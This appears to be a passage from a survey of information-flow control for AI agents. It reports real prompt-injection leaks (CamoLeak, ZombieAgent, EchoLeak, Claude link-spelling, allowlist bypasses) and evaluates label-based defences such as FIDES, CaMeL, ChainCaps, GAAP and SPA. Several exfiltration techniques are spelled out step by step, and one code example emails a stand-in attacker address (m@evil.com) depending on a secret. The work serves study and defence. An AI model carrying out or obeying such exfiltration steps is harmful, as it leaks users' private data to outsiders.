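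### What the same-origin policy leaves open

Browsers separate data by origin, which is the combination of a protocol, a host name and a port, as in https://bank.com. Under the same-origin policy, a page from attacker.com can't read or change a page from bank.com, even if the user has both pages open or the attacker's page displays the bank's in a frame.

The same-origin policy mainly restricts what a page can read and does little to restrict what it can send. Any page may load an image from any site, and the page's script chooses the image's address, which can contain whatever the script has read. The other site's server logs the address, even though the browser won't let the script examine the reply. Most large websites include scripts from other companies, for advertising or statistics, and these scripts run with the origin of the page that includes them. They can therefore read what the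 user types there and send it elsewhere without violating the policy. Websites can publish a list of permitted destinations, which browsers enforce, but the list applies to the whole page and doesn't depend on what a script has read.

Researchers tried to fill this gap with labels. JSFlow, which Daniel Hedin, Andrei Sabelfeld and colleagues presented in 2014, is an interpreter for JavaScript, the language of web pages. It labels every value and enforces the no-sensitive-upgrade rule, so it covers implicit flows. It was itself written in JavaScript and ran roughly a hundred times slower than a browser's own engine. Like every monitor with that rule, it also stops harmless scripts, unless a programmer marks in advance which variables will become secret. (FlowFox, a modified Firefox, avoided such stops by running each script once per security level.)

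COWL, which Deian Stefan, Edward Yang and colleagues published in the same year, labels whole pages and frames, much as Flume labels whole processes. For example, a page can pass a password to another company's strength-checking script. Once the script's frame has read the password, it can return a rating to the page but can't send anything to other sites. In test versions of Firefox and Chromium, users would hardly have noticed the difference in loading time. The World Wide Web Consortium, which sets web standards, published a first draft based on COWL in October 2015, but the draft never became a standard. Good performance was evidently not enough, since website developers would also have had to divide their pages into frames and decide on labels for the data that passed between them.

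Whether implicit flows are worth tracking depends partly on what real programs do. In 2019, Cristian-Alexandru Staicu and colleagues studied 56 JavaScript programs with known security problems, including code injection and privacy leaks. Tracking copies alone was enough for most of the 56 problems. For some privacy leaks, a monitor also had to track assignments that run because of a secret. The researchers found no case that depended on an assignment that never runs, like the one in the interview program. Tracking implicit flows also slowed the programs down, spread labels further and stopped more harmless runs.

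This only partly supports the choice that Costa and colleagues made for agents. The 56 programs had flaws or collected data too freely, and ordinary flaws rarely leak data through an assignment that never runs. But an attacker who knows that an agent's guard doesn't track implicit flows has a strong reason to use one. Like TaintDroid's test of 30 apps, the study gives a good idea of what explicit tracking catches when nobody is trying to evade it.

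### Origin limits for browser agents

An agent in a browser works across sites on the user's behalf, often with the user's logins, so it can carry data across the boundary that the same-origin policy protects. Google's response in December 2025 was to limit the sites that an agent in Chrome can reach during a task. According to Parker, a gating function that sees no web content decides which origins are relevant to the user's request and puts each into either a set that the agent may only read or a set where it may also click and type. If a page contains a frame from an origin in neither set, such as an advertisement, Chrome doesn't show the model that frame. The agent can't add a site to either set by itself, and before it opens a new site, a separate model checks whether the site is relevant.

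In effect, everything the agent reads during the session gets the same label, which lets the data go to any writable site. Suppose a user asks the agent to find a booking number in webmail and enter it on an airline's website. The mail site becomes readable and the airline's site writable. An instruction hidden in a customer review on the airline's site can't make the agent type the user's messages into a form at attacker.com. But because the sets limit only where data can go, not which data goes there, the instruction could try to make the agent paste another email into the airline's public review form.

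Chrome allows addresses the model has composed only if they are already publicly known. Neither this check nor OpenAI's similar one stops an agent from spelling out a code through the order in which it opens public pages on a readable site.

Chrome also requires the user's approval before the agent opens banking or medical sites on a fixed list or signs in with a stored password, which the model never sees. The agent is also supposed to pause for confirmation before purchases, payments and messages. These confirmations can stop a leak whose last step is a message, but they don't cover ordinary page visits.

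Google's first release was simpler than the design. It tracked only the writable set, and Google planned to adjust the rest after seeing how the limits affected users' tasks.

Independent tests followed soon afterwards. Roesner and Kohlbrenner (2026), in *Agentic Browsers and the Same-Origin Policy*, examined seven browsers with built-in or added agents in late January and early February 2026. They were looking for the following sequence:

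1. The user opens an attacker's page, which displays a page from another site in a frame.
2. The user asks the agent to summarise what is on the screen.
3. Hidden text tells the agent to include the framed page in its summary and to enter the summary in a form.
4. The form submits itself, and the attacker receives the other site's content.

The other site has to permit framing, and its cookie settings must let the user's login work inside the frame, which many sensitive sites prevent. But the attack can also work in reverse, with a malicious advertisement stealing from the page around it. Roesner and Kohlbrenner carried out the data theft on OpenAI's ChatGPT Atlas in its agent mode. They found that Chrome with Gemini, Anthropic's Claude for Chrome and Perplexity's Comet also met the conditions for it, provided an injected instruction succeeded. OpenAI declined their report, saying it did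 not include an end-to-end prompt injection attack.

Roesner and Kohlbrenner argued that in these browsers the same-origin policy is now only as strong as the model's resistance to injected instructions. Before agents, the browser's code enforced the policy regardless of what any text on a page said. Their point is different from the objection, which concerns how easily someone can deceive the model. Chrome's presence on the list is consistent with a first version that did not yet limit reading, but the tests don't establish that this was the reason.

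The browsers differed widely. Brave, Edge and Firefox gave their agents limited information about a page in a fixed format, which made them safer but less useful. The Claude for Chrome extension could insert its own scripts into pages, and Roesner and Kohlbrenner advised particular caution with it. They also found that some agents could read passwords that the browser displays as dots. As of April 2026, then, browser makers had no common rule for what an agent may carry from one site to another.

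### From processes to a model's context

The slowdowns that held back earlier trackers are not a problem for agents. Flume's monitor handled 753 system calls to display one wiki page, and each took up to 0.3 milliseconds longer than on plain Linux. An agent makes perhaps a few dozen tool calls in a task, and the model usually takes seconds to generate each one, so comparing two labels before every call adds practically no delay.

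The boundary doesn't carry over as easily. The kernel can label a process because every message in or out passes through the kernel, but it can't tell which of the process's outputs came from which input. *Laminar* addresses this weakness by combining operating-system labels with labels inside programs. TaintDroid could track data inside an app because the interpreter ran one operation at a time, with known inputs and a known result. A language model has no such steps because it computes each word from its entire context. An email, a web page and a password in the same conversation can all affect the next tool call, so for a label system the context is like a single process that has read all three.

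The older systems suggest keeping separate data in separate processes as a remedy. Asbestos gave each user's session its own event process. HiStar can run a service on sensitive data in a labelled copy of the original process, so the original never acquires the label. The side conversations in the calculus of Garby and colleagues serve the same purpose. This separation works well when an agent's task divides into parts that need different data, and less well when the task is to combine the data.

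Small trusted programs are harder to copy in agent systems. HiStar's wrap needs only 110 lines of code because it doesn't have to analyze the scanner's report. It passes the report to the owner of the files, who is allowed to see all of it anyway. The launcher for Flume's wiki likewise returns a page only to a user who is allowed to read it. But an agent that answers a customer's email has to send something derived from private data to a person who isn't allowed to see that data. A program that approves such a reply has to evaluate its content, which no short piece of code can do reliably.

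The old methods still apply directly where a boundary can remain around the whole agent. Zeldovich and colleagues used HiStar to separate a company's internal network from the internet on one computer. Data from the internet carries the label i, and data from the internal network carries the label v. The system blocks data labelled v from reaching the internet and data labelled i from entering the internal network, unless an owner of the label permits it. Two agents, one for each network, could work under this rule without changes to the model, but a single agent that read from both networks in one conversation would carry both labels and could send to neither network.

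## Case reports: leaks found in deployed assistants

Since 2023, security researchers have repeatedly tricked commercial assistants into sending private data to outside servers. In the simplest demonstrations, the assistant put the data in a web address and then requested that address. As vendors blocked this method, researchers began spreading the data over many requests, each to an address that someone had prepared before the assistant read anything private. This worked against GitHub's Copilot Chat and OpenAI's ChatGPT in 2025 and against Anthropic's Claude in 2026.

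### CamoLeak: a private text spelled out in images

Legit Security's *CamoLeak* describes a flaw that one of the company's researchers found in June 2025 in Copilot Chat, an assistant that answers questions about software projects hosted on GitHub. An outsider proposes a change to a project and adds instructions in a comment that GitHub hides from readers. When another user asks Copilot about the proposal, the assistant reads the comment and follows the instructions with that user's permissions, which may cover private projects.

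Browsers request images automatically, so an attacker could most easily have sent the stolen text out by putting it in an image address. GitHub had blocked this method. The chat page could load images only from GitHub's own domains, and GitHub's image proxy, Camo, fetched outside images only from addresses that GitHub had already signed cryptographically. The assistant couldn't sign an address it generated during a conversation.

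The researcher therefore had GitHub sign a set of image addresses in advance, one for each letter and symbol, and put them in the hidden comment. Copilot then reproduced the private text as a row of these images. Each image was a single transparent pixel, so the user saw nothing while the researcher's server received the text one character at a time. One demonstration extracted the description of an unpatched vulnerability from a private project. In another, Copilot searched the victim's code for a cloud access key and sent out the result.

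GitHub reported that it had fixed the vulnerability as of 14 August 2025 by turning off images in Copilot Chat altogether. Press coverage listed in OECD's *GitHub Copilot Chat Vulnerability Exposes Private Code and Secrets* (2025) dates from 8 October.

Camo's signature check passed every image because it tests who signed an address and not why the assistant chose it. A tracker limited to explicit flows would have missed the leak too, since the addresses came from the outsider's comment and contained no private text. (It could have caught an earlier version, in which Copilot put the encoded text into a link for the user to click.)

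A conservative tracker would have applied the private project's label to Copilot's whole answer. But the user is allowed to read that project, so a check made when the answer reached the user would have allowed it. To catch the leak, the label has to stay on the answer until the browser displays it, and the check has to treat each image as a message to the outside server behind the proxy.

### ZombieAgent: one address for each character and position

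ChatGPT can connect to services such as Gmail and Google Drive. According to The Record's *OpenAI fixes zero-click ShadowLeak vulnerability*, an attack called ShadowLeak used hidden text in an email to direct ChatGPT's research agent to find an employee's name and address in the inbox and open a lookup page on the attacker's server. OpenAI responded to such attacks by forbidding ChatGPT to modify the URLs it opens.

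*ZombieAgent*, published by the security company Radware in January 2026, describes a way around that rule. The attacker's email supplies a complete URL for every character, and the agent opens the ones that spell out the secret. ChatGPT never modifies a URL, so the rule allows every request.

Radware also solved the problem of out-of-order requests by preparing a separate address for each character in each position. The four-digit code from the first section would need 40 addresses instead of ten, but the attacker could then put the requests in order. Repeated digits would also use different addresses, so the ban on repeat visits that Embrace The Red proposed would not stop this version.

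The email's label lists everyone allowed to read it, including the attacker who sent it. Addresses copied from the email keep that label, so an explicit-flow tracker would have let the agent send them back to the attacker. A cautious tracker would have stopped the first request because the agent had also read messages the attacker wasn't allowed to see, but such trackers usually cause label creep.

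A second part of the attack made the leak persistent. OpenAI did not let ChatGPT use its long-term memory in a chat after it had used a connected service, but ChatGPT could still use memory first and then a connected service. Radware used a shared file to plant instructions in memory, and from then on ChatGPT fetched the attacker's email before answering each message. An integrity label stored with each memory could have marked those instructions as untrusted in every later chat.

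Radware reported the flaw on 26 September 2025. Bugcrowd, which handles such reports for OpenAI, reproduced it four days later, and OpenAI fixed it on 16 December. The news aggregator Particle.news reported in *Radware's 'ZombieAgent' Bypasses ChatGPT Fixes, Forcing New OpenAI Restrictions* that OpenAI restricted the opening of links from emails, except well-known public ones. This resembles the public-index check that OpenAI described in January 2026 without naming ZombieAgent. Radware's scheme would need 360 indexed pages to get a ten-character secret of letters and digits past that check.

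### The same method against Claude

Anthropic had a similar rule for Claude's tool for opening web pages. Claude could open only addresses that the user had typed, that a web search had returned, or that appeared on a page it had already fetched. In July 2026 Ayush Paul showed that the last of these was enough to leak data. His site offered a link for each letter and told Claude to spell out the user's name to reach a profile (Willison, 2026). By following the links, Claude gave away the user's name, home city and employer, which it knew from its memory of earlier chats.

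In *The Read-Only Lie*, the blogger dyb counted 27 links on each page, or 4.75 bits per request, and estimated that the leak took about 30 requests and carried at most 143 bits. Claude had inferred Paul's home city from the name of a high-school hackathon. Paul had never told Claude the city, so a filter that searched outgoing requests for stored facts would have had no entry for it. A label could cover the inferred fact, but it would also have to cover Claude's choice of links to stop the leak.

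Anthropic said it had already found the problem internally. It removed the tool's ability to follow links on pages it has fetched.

Embrace The Red described using one address per character as early as 2023. *Exfiltration of personal information from ChatGPT via prompt injection* (2024) reports a character-by-character leak that was limited to ten characters because ChatGPT then opened at most ten addresses per prompt. Such a cap is weaker against a larger set of addresses because each visit carries more information. A visit carries 5.2 bits with 36 addresses, one for each letter and digit, and 12 bits with 4,096.

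### EchoLeak: four permitted steps

Microsoft 365 Copilot answers employees' questions using their organization's emails, files and chats. Ravia (2025), in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability*, describes how the security group Aim Labs extracted data from it with an email from outside. "Zero-click" means that the victim does nothing except use the assistant normally. The secret left in one request, but it got there by composition, and each step passed a different check:

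1. The email arrived. Microsoft's classifier looked for instructions aimed at an AI, but the email appeared to address its human recipient.
2. An employee asked Copilot a question, and Copilot retrieved the email along with internal material. The email covered many workplace topics, so that it would match many questions.
3. Following the email, Copilot put the most sensitive information it could find into an image address. A filter removed outside links from Copilot's answers, but it did not recognize one way of writing them.
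4. The browser requested the image. It accepted only approved domains, but one of them belonged to a Microsoft Teams service that fetches other addresses on request, and this service forwarded the data to the researchers' server.

Anything in Copilot's context could have leaked this way, including earlier chat messages and retrieved files. Aim Labs reported the flaw to Microsoft in January 2025, Microsoft finished patching it in May, and Aim Labs published its report on 11 June, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Microsoft 365 Copilot*. Ravia writes that Microsoft confirmed the flaw had affected no customers.

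EchoLeak was an explicit flow because the secret was in the address. An explicit-flow tracker would have detected it if the label survived the model's copying. Whether the tracker would then have blocked the request depends on which destination it checked. The browser was contacting Microsoft, which already stored the data, and only the address inside the request showed that the data would go beyond Microsoft.

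Integrity labels would have allowed an earlier intervention. The email came from outside the organization and influenced the image address, so a rule against automatic requests influenced by untrusted content would have blocked the image request, whatever data it contained. Ravia makes a related point with the term "LLM scope violation", which means that text from an untrusted source directs the model to data that the text's author has no right to see.

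### Approved destinations that pass data on

Lists of approved domains failed in several other products. Willison describes four cases in which researchers found a way to receive data through an address on such a list:

| Product and date | Approved destination | How the data got out | Vendor's response |
|---|---|---|---|
| Salesforce Agentforce, September 2025 | A domain whose registration had expired | The researchers registered it themselves | Corrected the list and restricted the links the agent can generate |
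| Google Antigravity, November 2025 | A public service for logging web requests | The service lets anyone create a log and read it | Listed this type of leak as a known issue and was working on it |
| Superhuman, January 2026 | Google's documents domain | An online form on that domain stored the data | Issued a fix |
| Claude Cowork, January 2026 | Anthropic's own interface for developers | The agent uploaded files to the attacker's Anthropic account | Tightened permissions, according to dyb |

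These failures also matter for label systems, because a label check has to determine who can read data sent to an address. The domain name isn't enough to determine this if the user and the attacker can both have accounts there. For Claude Cowork, the check would have had to identify which account received the upload.

Data may leak even when an agent sends a message only to its own user. In May 2026, Willison reported that Microsoft's Copilot Cowork could email the user without asking for approval. A label check would permit the message because the user may read their own data. But the message could contain images hosted on an outside server, and opening it sent data to that server. That data could include a ready-made download link for a file in the user's OneDrive storage. A leakage budget would count only the bytes of the link, although the link gives an outsider the whole file.

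Vendors can also overlook a channel. OpenAI restricts direct outside access from the environment where ChatGPT runs code, but Check Point Research's *ChatGPT data leakage via a hidden outbound channel* describes a way around the restriction. The researchers sent a summary of a user's content to an external server, and ChatGPT showed no warning. A label check placed only on known channels would have missed that transfer.

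### Demonstrations, thefts and success rates

Each report shows that a particular product could leak data, at least until the vendor fixed the flaw. The reports give little evidence of how often an attack would succeed, because researchers choose the wording and publish what works. Radware reports a 100% success rate for its improved attack but doesn't give the number of attempts. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) quotes another attack, which outside researchers reported in 2025 and which worked 50% of the time with one particular user request. OpenAI adds that most of the attacks it knows of fail because the model refuses.

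Tests of a bare model can also exaggerate the risk to a product's users. In *The Framing Gap* (2026), injected instructions extracted secrets from a model in up to 100% of trials when the researchers accessed it directly, but in none of 48 valid trials with the ChatGPT product. The researchers could not tell which part of the product made the difference. The 48 trials also do not rule out leaks, because an attack that worked 6% of the time would still have about a 5% chance of failing in all of them.

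Counting actual thefts is harder still. According to the AI-generated summary in OECD's *ZombieAgent Vulnerability Enables Data Theft and Account Takeover in ChatGPT* (2026), thefts occurred before the fix. Radware's own account describes only demonstrations, so the summary is poor evidence that anyone exploited the flaw. The lack of known victims is also weak evidence that no data was stolen. ZombieAgent's requests came from OpenAI's servers, where the customer's own network monitoring could not detect them. In CamoLeak, the proxy handled only validly signed image requests. Microsoft was better placed to look for victims of EchoLeak, because the data passed through its own services.

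### The lethal trifecta

Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, drew a general rule from more than a dozen such cases. An attacker can steal data from an agent that has access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to communicate with the outside. Willison advises people who connect their own tools to avoid combining all three. He considers a filter that catches 95% of attacks an inadequate substitute, because attackers can keep rewording their instructions.

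The rule is simple to apply because it depends on an agent's tools, not on what happens in a run. It is also stricter than labels need to be, since a labelled agent may have all three capabilities as long as no single run combines them in a forbidden way.

Outside communication is generally the easiest capability to remove, according to Willison, and vendors' fixes usually restrict it. Tighter restrictions disable more of the assistant's useful functions. GitHub disabled all images in Copilot Chat. As dyb points out, an agent that can't choose any part of an address can't browse documentation spread over several pages. One compromise dyb suggests is to let the agent follow links only on sites the user has named, which requires an extra confirmation. OpenAI decided against relying on a list of trusted sites, partly because people who see frequent warnings can learn to click through them. Trusted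 sites may also redirect the agent elsewhere.

An agent often can't do its task without reading untrusted content. The security company Zenity Labs showed that a customer's support request could make Cursor, a coding tool, send out a secret from a developer's project. Cursor recommended connecting only to sources of trusted content. A team that wants its agent to work on support requests can't follow this advice, because outsiders write the requests.

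An email assistant is useless without private data, but a coding agent can often work with less of it. Willison suggests giving a coding agent only credentials for test accounts with strict spending limits, so that anyone who stole the credentials could do only limited damage.

Most repairs close one route between the three capabilities but leave all three in place, so new routes keep turning up. A year after EchoLeak, *Attackers tricked Copilot into leaking sensitive data through Bing* (Okemwa, 2026) reported a flaw that exposed company files and login codes. In August 2026, Atlassian fixed a flaw that let one crafted link extract company data through its assistant Rovo (Mascellino, 2026, *Researchers Uncover RovoBlast Vulnerability in Atlassian AI Assistant*). The same month, TechRadar's *Experts manage to hack Microsoft Copilot by continually asking it questions* described CoSnitch, a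 chain of Copilot flaws that the security company Varonis found. CoSnitch used malicious links and planted memories, and Microsoft patched it on its servers. On 5 December, *Hackers build zero-click attacks in Microsoft Copilot* (Fadilpašić, 2026) reported three more methods of attacking Copilot, under the name ReLeak.

### A leak across ten sessions without an attacker

The lethal trifecta is a rule about attacks, so it doesn't cover accidents. *A missing config file triggered an AI agent to leak passwords* (Udinmwen, 22 November 2026) describes a coding assistant doing a routine code review. When the assistant couldn't find its configuration file, it collected all the computer's environment variables (settings that programs share, which often include credentials) and leaked working passwords. Over ten sessions, it repeatedly read entire configuration files and leaked production passwords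 and access tokens for a personnel system.

A missing file triggered the leak, so shielding the assistant from untrusted content would not have prevented it. Udinmwen points to agents' lack of institutional memory and their disregard of past warnings. Labels don't depend on the agent's memory, because a label the operator puts on a stored password applies again in each new session. But the operator would have to label every copy, since a label on the configuration file alone would not have protected the same password in an environment variable.

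## Experiments: agents that carry labels through their tool calls

A label on a password helps only if it stays attached while an agent copies, summarises and forwards the password. Since 2025, researchers have built agents that keep labels attached and check them before each tool call. Their experiments measure how many attacks this stops and how much ordinary work it prevents. Most of the attacks are prompt injections that try to cause one forbidden action, but several designs from 2026 address secrets leaked through a series of individually acceptable actions.

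### What FIDES checks before a call

Costa and colleagues built FIDES around the ordinary agent loop. Each message in the conversation has an integrity label, "trusted" or "untrusted", and a confidentiality label that lists the permitted readers. Wrappers around the tools label each field of a result separately, so the date of an email can be labeled trusted even when its text is untrusted. The conversation's label combines the labels of its messages.

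Before a call runs, FIDES compares the labels with the tool's policy. There are two basic rules:

1. The agent may take a consequential action, such as paying a bill, only if the choice of action and its important arguments rest on trusted data.
2. The agent may send data only to people on the data's list of readers.

Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, reuse these policies and explain that a tool that sends data out must satisfy only one of the two rules. They reason that if nothing untrusted has influenced the agent, the user probably meant to send the data. This prevents data theft through injected instructions, but not accidental leaks. If the operator had labelled the environment file in the first section's example as trusted, this policy would have let the agent copy the credentials into the shared document.

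Reading a single untrusted email would make the whole conversation untrusted and block most later actions. To avoid this, FIDES hides a tool result in a variable, but only when the result's label is stricter than the conversation's. The model can pass the variable on without reading it. It can also send the variable to an isolated model, which has no tools and whose answer goes into a new variable with the same restrictions. If that isn't enough, the model can open the variable, and the conversation then takes on the variable's label.

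### One email task from start to finish

Suppose Alex asks the agent to read the three latest emails and, if one requests a meeting, add it to the calendar. One email is a genuine invitation. In another, an attacker tells the agent to forward Alex's mail to an outside address.

1. The agent calls the email tool. The texts come back untrusted, so FIDES stores them in a variable, and the conversation stays trusted.
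2. The agent asks the isolated model whether any of the emails requests a meeting, and allows only "yes" or "no" as an answer. The isolated model reads the attacker's instruction but has no tool with which to carry it out.
3. The agent opens the variable that holds the answer and sees "yes". One untrusted bit has now entered the conversation, which a policy can tolerate because FIDES's labels also record how much an answer can hold.
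4. The agent has the isolated model extract the date, time and participants into another variable.
5. The agent passes that variable to the calendar tool, and FIDES allows the call.

The attacker's instruction never reaches the model that chooses the tools. The attacker might still get the isolated model to extract a wrong date or an extra participant. Preventing that would take a stricter policy that also requires trusted event details. Without variables, the agent would have read all three emails itself, and the first rule would have blocked even the genuine calendar entry.

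### CaMeL: writing the program before reading the data

CaMeL, which Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues published in 2025, separates planning from data more sharply, because its planning model writes the whole program, in a restricted form of Python, before any tool returns data. To interpret untrusted text, the program calls a second model that has no tools. The planning model doesn't see the data tools return, so an email can't add a step to the program, though it can still supply a bad value, such as the attacker's bank account, to an existing step. CaMeL therefore records where each value came from and who may read it, and each tool has a policy that checks these records.

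In normal mode, a result inherits the records of the values that went into it. Strict mode adds the records of the conditions that determined whether a line ran. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, give an example in which this matters:

`if account.balance > threshold: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")`

The message's text is fixed and contains nothing secret, but the recipient can infer something about the balance from its arrival. When CaMeL tracks the condition, the email inherits the balance's restrictions and the interpreter blocks it. Strict mode still misses the untaken branch described earlier.

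### AgentDojo in 2025

Most of these systems have scores on AgentDojo, a benchmark with 97 user tasks in a simulated office, Slack workspace, travel service and bank. For each attack, the benchmark plants instructions in data that the agent will read. Built-in tests then check whether the agent completed the user's task and whether it achieved the attacker's goal.

Costa and colleagues ran it with GPT-4o. The basic agent in the table is an ordinary agent loop to which they added labels. The completion rates are averages over the four environments with no attack.

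| Agent | Successful attacks, checks off | Successful attacks, checks on | Tasks completed, checks off | Tasks completed, checks on |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Basic agent | 152 | 0 | 84% | 42% |
| FIDES | 21 | 0 | 61% | 50% |

The zeros come from a manual review. AgentDojo's own tests counted three successful attacks against FIDES with checks on. Costa and colleagues rejected such cases partly because the policy deliberately allows some messages.

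Many of the uncompleted tasks failed because the policy worked as intended. Several banking tasks, for example, require the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it, which is also what an attacker would want. Other tasks passed partly by luck. In one, the agent was supposed to change the user's password if it found a suspicious transaction. FIDES had hidden the transaction descriptions, so the model changed the password based on the amounts alone and passed the test.

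These experiments provide more evidence about integrity than about secrecy. Costa and colleagues hid results in variables only when the data was untrusted, regardless of whether it was confidential. They also left out the restricted answer formats used in the calendar example, which they considered unnecessary for most of the benchmark's tasks.

### Planners that take the labels into account

FIDES doesn't show its model the policies, so the model sometimes opens a variable unnecessarily and then can't finish the task. Kolluri and colleagues, who also work mainly at Microsoft, built a planner called Prudentia on top of FIDES. Prudentia shows the model the conversation's label and which tools require a trusted one. Before opening a variable, the model has to explain why it needs to and list the calls it plans to make afterwards. The model can also ask the user to endorse the variable's contents.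 If an email contains a to-do list with ten items, one endorsement replaces ten separate approvals.

The table below gives the AgentDojo results with GPT-5. All four agents could ask the user to approve a call, and the last column is the total number of these requests in the tasks they completed.

| Agent | Completed without any request | Completed with unlimited requests | Requests to the user |
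|---|---|---|---|
| Basic agent, which asks before every consequential call | 35.1% | 72.3% | 52.0 |
| Basic agent with labels | 43.4% | 72.3% | 40.4 |
| FIDES | 57.1% | 78.9% | 41.3 |
| Prudentia | 72.7% | 80.0% | 7.3 |

Prudentia completed about as many tasks with no help as the basic agent did with unlimited approvals. But the benefit depends on the model. With the older GPT-4o, Prudentia completed 42.5% of tasks unaided, compared with 50.3% for FIDES. Kolluri and colleagues estimate that Prudentia with GPT-4o cost about four to six cents per task, roughly four to ten times as much as the basic labelled agent.

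In a second benchmark, WASP, attackers plant instructions on simulated GitLab and Reddit pages. These instructions diverted the basic agent in 15% to 61% of cases, depending on the model and site, and never diverted Prudentia. The user's tasks were only to post a comment or upvote a post, so the agent could do them without reading any untrusted text.

Randori, an agent that Garby and colleagues wrote in their LLMbda calculus, resisted all but 2 of 1,296 attacks. The runs used AgentDojo's banking environment, with 16 tasks, 9 attacks, three models and three repetitions. Both successful attacks used the same attack on the same task with GPT-5.2. In that task, the user asks the agent to read a text file and make the payment it describes, but the attacker has replaced the file's contents with a different payment request. Randori has to endorse the file to do the task, and labels can't distinguish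 a genuine bill from a forged one because both arrive by the same route.

Randori completed 36 of 48 banking runs with GPT-5.2 when label checks were on and there was no attack. Garby and colleagues also reran CaMeL with GPT-5.2, and it completed 32 of 48 runs with its policies off and 18 with them on.

Planning before reading stops many attacks without any labels. According to Garby and colleagues, 97 of the 144 pairs of banking task and attack need a tool call or file read that the program for the user's task would never contain. When they reran CaMeL with policies off, only 5 of 622 attacks succeeded. Girrens and Wang (2026), in *SPA*, found much the same on all of AgentDojo with an agent that plans first. With label checks off, 4 of 949 attacks succeeded, and with checks on, none did. The checks also reduced the share of tasks completed from 53% to 29%. AgentDojo's attack scores therefore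 no longer show much about what labels add to an agent that plans first, though the benchmark still shows how much they reduce task completion.

### ChainCaps: a list of places where a value may go

*ChainCaps* (Jiang, Yang and colleagues, 2026) starts from the composition problem, in which tool calls that are each permitted can together leak data. For example, an agent reads a salary spreadsheet, fetches industry figures from the web, summarises both and emails the summary to a distribution list, which sends the salaries outside the company.

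In ChainCaps, each value carries a budget, which here means the set of sinks it may still reach. When a tool t turns the inputs x₁ to xₖ into an output y, the output's budget is

B(y) = Pass(t) ∩ B(x₁) ∩ … ∩ B(xₖ),

where Pass(t) is a limit that the operator sets for the tool. If the operator allows the salaries only on the user's screen and the web figures both on the screen and in emails, the summary gets

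{screen} ∩ {screen, email} = {screen},

and ChainCaps blocks the email. A budget can only shrink as data passes through tools, unless someone issues a signed permission that is valid for one particular release.

FIDES's lists of readers also shrink by intersection, but a budget specifies operations and places, such as sending to one web address or writing to one folder. An operator can therefore let a person see a figure on the screen but not receive it by email.

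The model's conversation also has a budget, and everything the model writes inherits it, as with the cautious tracker described earlier. But Jiang and colleagues make no claim about implicit flows. They also exclude covert channels, malicious tools, mistakes in the operator's settings and anything outside the proxy that carries the tool calls.

The team tested 56 attack tasks and 26 harmless ones with five models, including Claude Opus 4.6 and GPT-5.1. Without ChainCaps, between 25% and 68% of attacks succeeded, depending on the model. With it, at most 4.8% succeeded, and the agents still completed 96% to 100% of the harmless tasks. In some of the successful attacks, the agent wrote a script to run later or passed data from one shell command to another, where the proxy couldn't follow it.

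Harder harmless tasks triggered false alarms in 45% of cases. Resetting the conversation's budget between tasks lowered this to 20%, but a reset is safe only if the model no longer has the earlier conversation.

Jiang and colleagues also report that ChainCaps blocked far more recorded attacks than FIDES, but they tested a simplified stand-in for FIDES that gives each value a single secrecy level. The result is therefore weak evidence about how the real FIDES would compare.

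### GAAP: remembering what a service already knows

*TaintDroid* lost its labels when data left the phone and came back in a server's reply. *An AI Agent Execution Environment to Safeguard User Data* (Stanley, Verma and colleagues, 2026) addresses this problem with GAAP, a system that logs every private item it discloses and who received it. If an agent gives an airline the user's passport number and later fetches a booking confirmation from the airline, GAAP labels the confirmation as possibly containing the passport number. GAAP then warns the user before the agent forwards the confirmation to a friend.

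GAAP treats the model as completely untrusted. The model writes a plan in a small language that has only tool calls and conditions, and GAAP analyses the plan before and during execution. Private items such as a date of birth are kept in a separate store, and the plan refers to them by name. GAAP labels each item with its name, and the label follows the item through the plan. When a condition depends on a private item, GAAP also labels every instruction on both branches until they rejoin. It can do this because it has the whole text of the plan, including the branch that doesn't run.

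This covers the choice channel as long as the choice is part of the plan. Suppose a plan looks up the code 7294 and uses conditions to choose one public page to request for each digit. All the requests carry the label "code", so GAAP would ask the user whether the website may receive the code, although no address contains any part of it. If the user lets the model see the code, GAAP puts the label on every call in the model's later plans. A blocked call returns an error with the same label and the plan continues, so an outsider can't infer the secret from where the run stopped.

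Stanley and colleagues tried seven injection attacks on each of 20 tasks, using GPT-5.6 Sol. GAAP stopped every attack. Five of the seven attacks succeeded on at least some tasks against an agent whose calls a second model judged one by one.

To measure how much usefulness GAAP loses, the team ran AgentDojo and another benchmark, AgentDyn, in which tasks take unexpected turns. GAAP completed about as many AgentDojo tasks as an unprotected agent and 10% fewer on AgentDyn. In both tests, the researchers assumed the user approved every disclosure, so the results include no losses from refusals. Running the two benchmarks with GAAP cost 2.9 times as much as with the unprotected agent, and the average task took 188 seconds instead of 28.

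GAAP doesn't protect private data that the user types into the request, and it doesn't hide the timing or order of the user's requests. It also protects only confidentiality, so an injected instruction can still make the agent take harmful actions that don't disclose private data.

### SPA: labels on stored results

An agent with a memory can act on something it read in an earlier session. In an example from Girrens and Wang, the agent saves an invoice that contains an attacker's account number, and the next day the user asks it to pay "the invoice we discussed yesterday". A secret can leak the same way if the agent stores it in one session and sends it in the next.

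The SPA system writes one complete plan for each request and checks the labels, including those on conditions, before any tool runs. A rejection therefore can't depend on what the tools would have returned. After the run, SPA stores each result with its label. When the user makes another request, the planning model receives only a description of the stored results. The new plan can retrieve a stored result, which keeps its label.

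Girrens and Wang turned the AgentDojo tasks into conversations with several requests. With GPT-5.4-nano and label checks turned on, SPA retrieved the right stored result 90% of the time when one existed. The checks lowered task completion from 62.5% to 35.3%, mainly because many legitimate tasks use outside data to decide on an important action.

Attack success was 0.3% without the checks and 0.2% with them. It was only 0.6% even when the planner could read the stored contents. Girrens and Wang conclude that AgentDojo's attacks barely test delayed leaks, because few of the injected instructions are designed to have an effect later. SPA assumes that the user's request is honest and that the operator has set the policies correctly.

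### FlowSeal: leaking a secret by leaving it alone

In September 2026, Shim, Karim and colleagues (2026), in *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow*, published attacks that use neither injected instructions nor compromised tools. In their example, Jane's assistant knows Mark's medical diagnosis, and Mark's former wife, Emily, wants to find it out. Three approaches worked:

- Emily shares a document and asks the assistant to fill in its part, which makes the disclosure look like teamwork.
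- She mixes true and false statements about Mark and asks the assistant to clean up the list. The entries it refuses to delete are the true ones.
- She asks for the information on one channel and receives it on another, so that the assistant doesn't connect the two.

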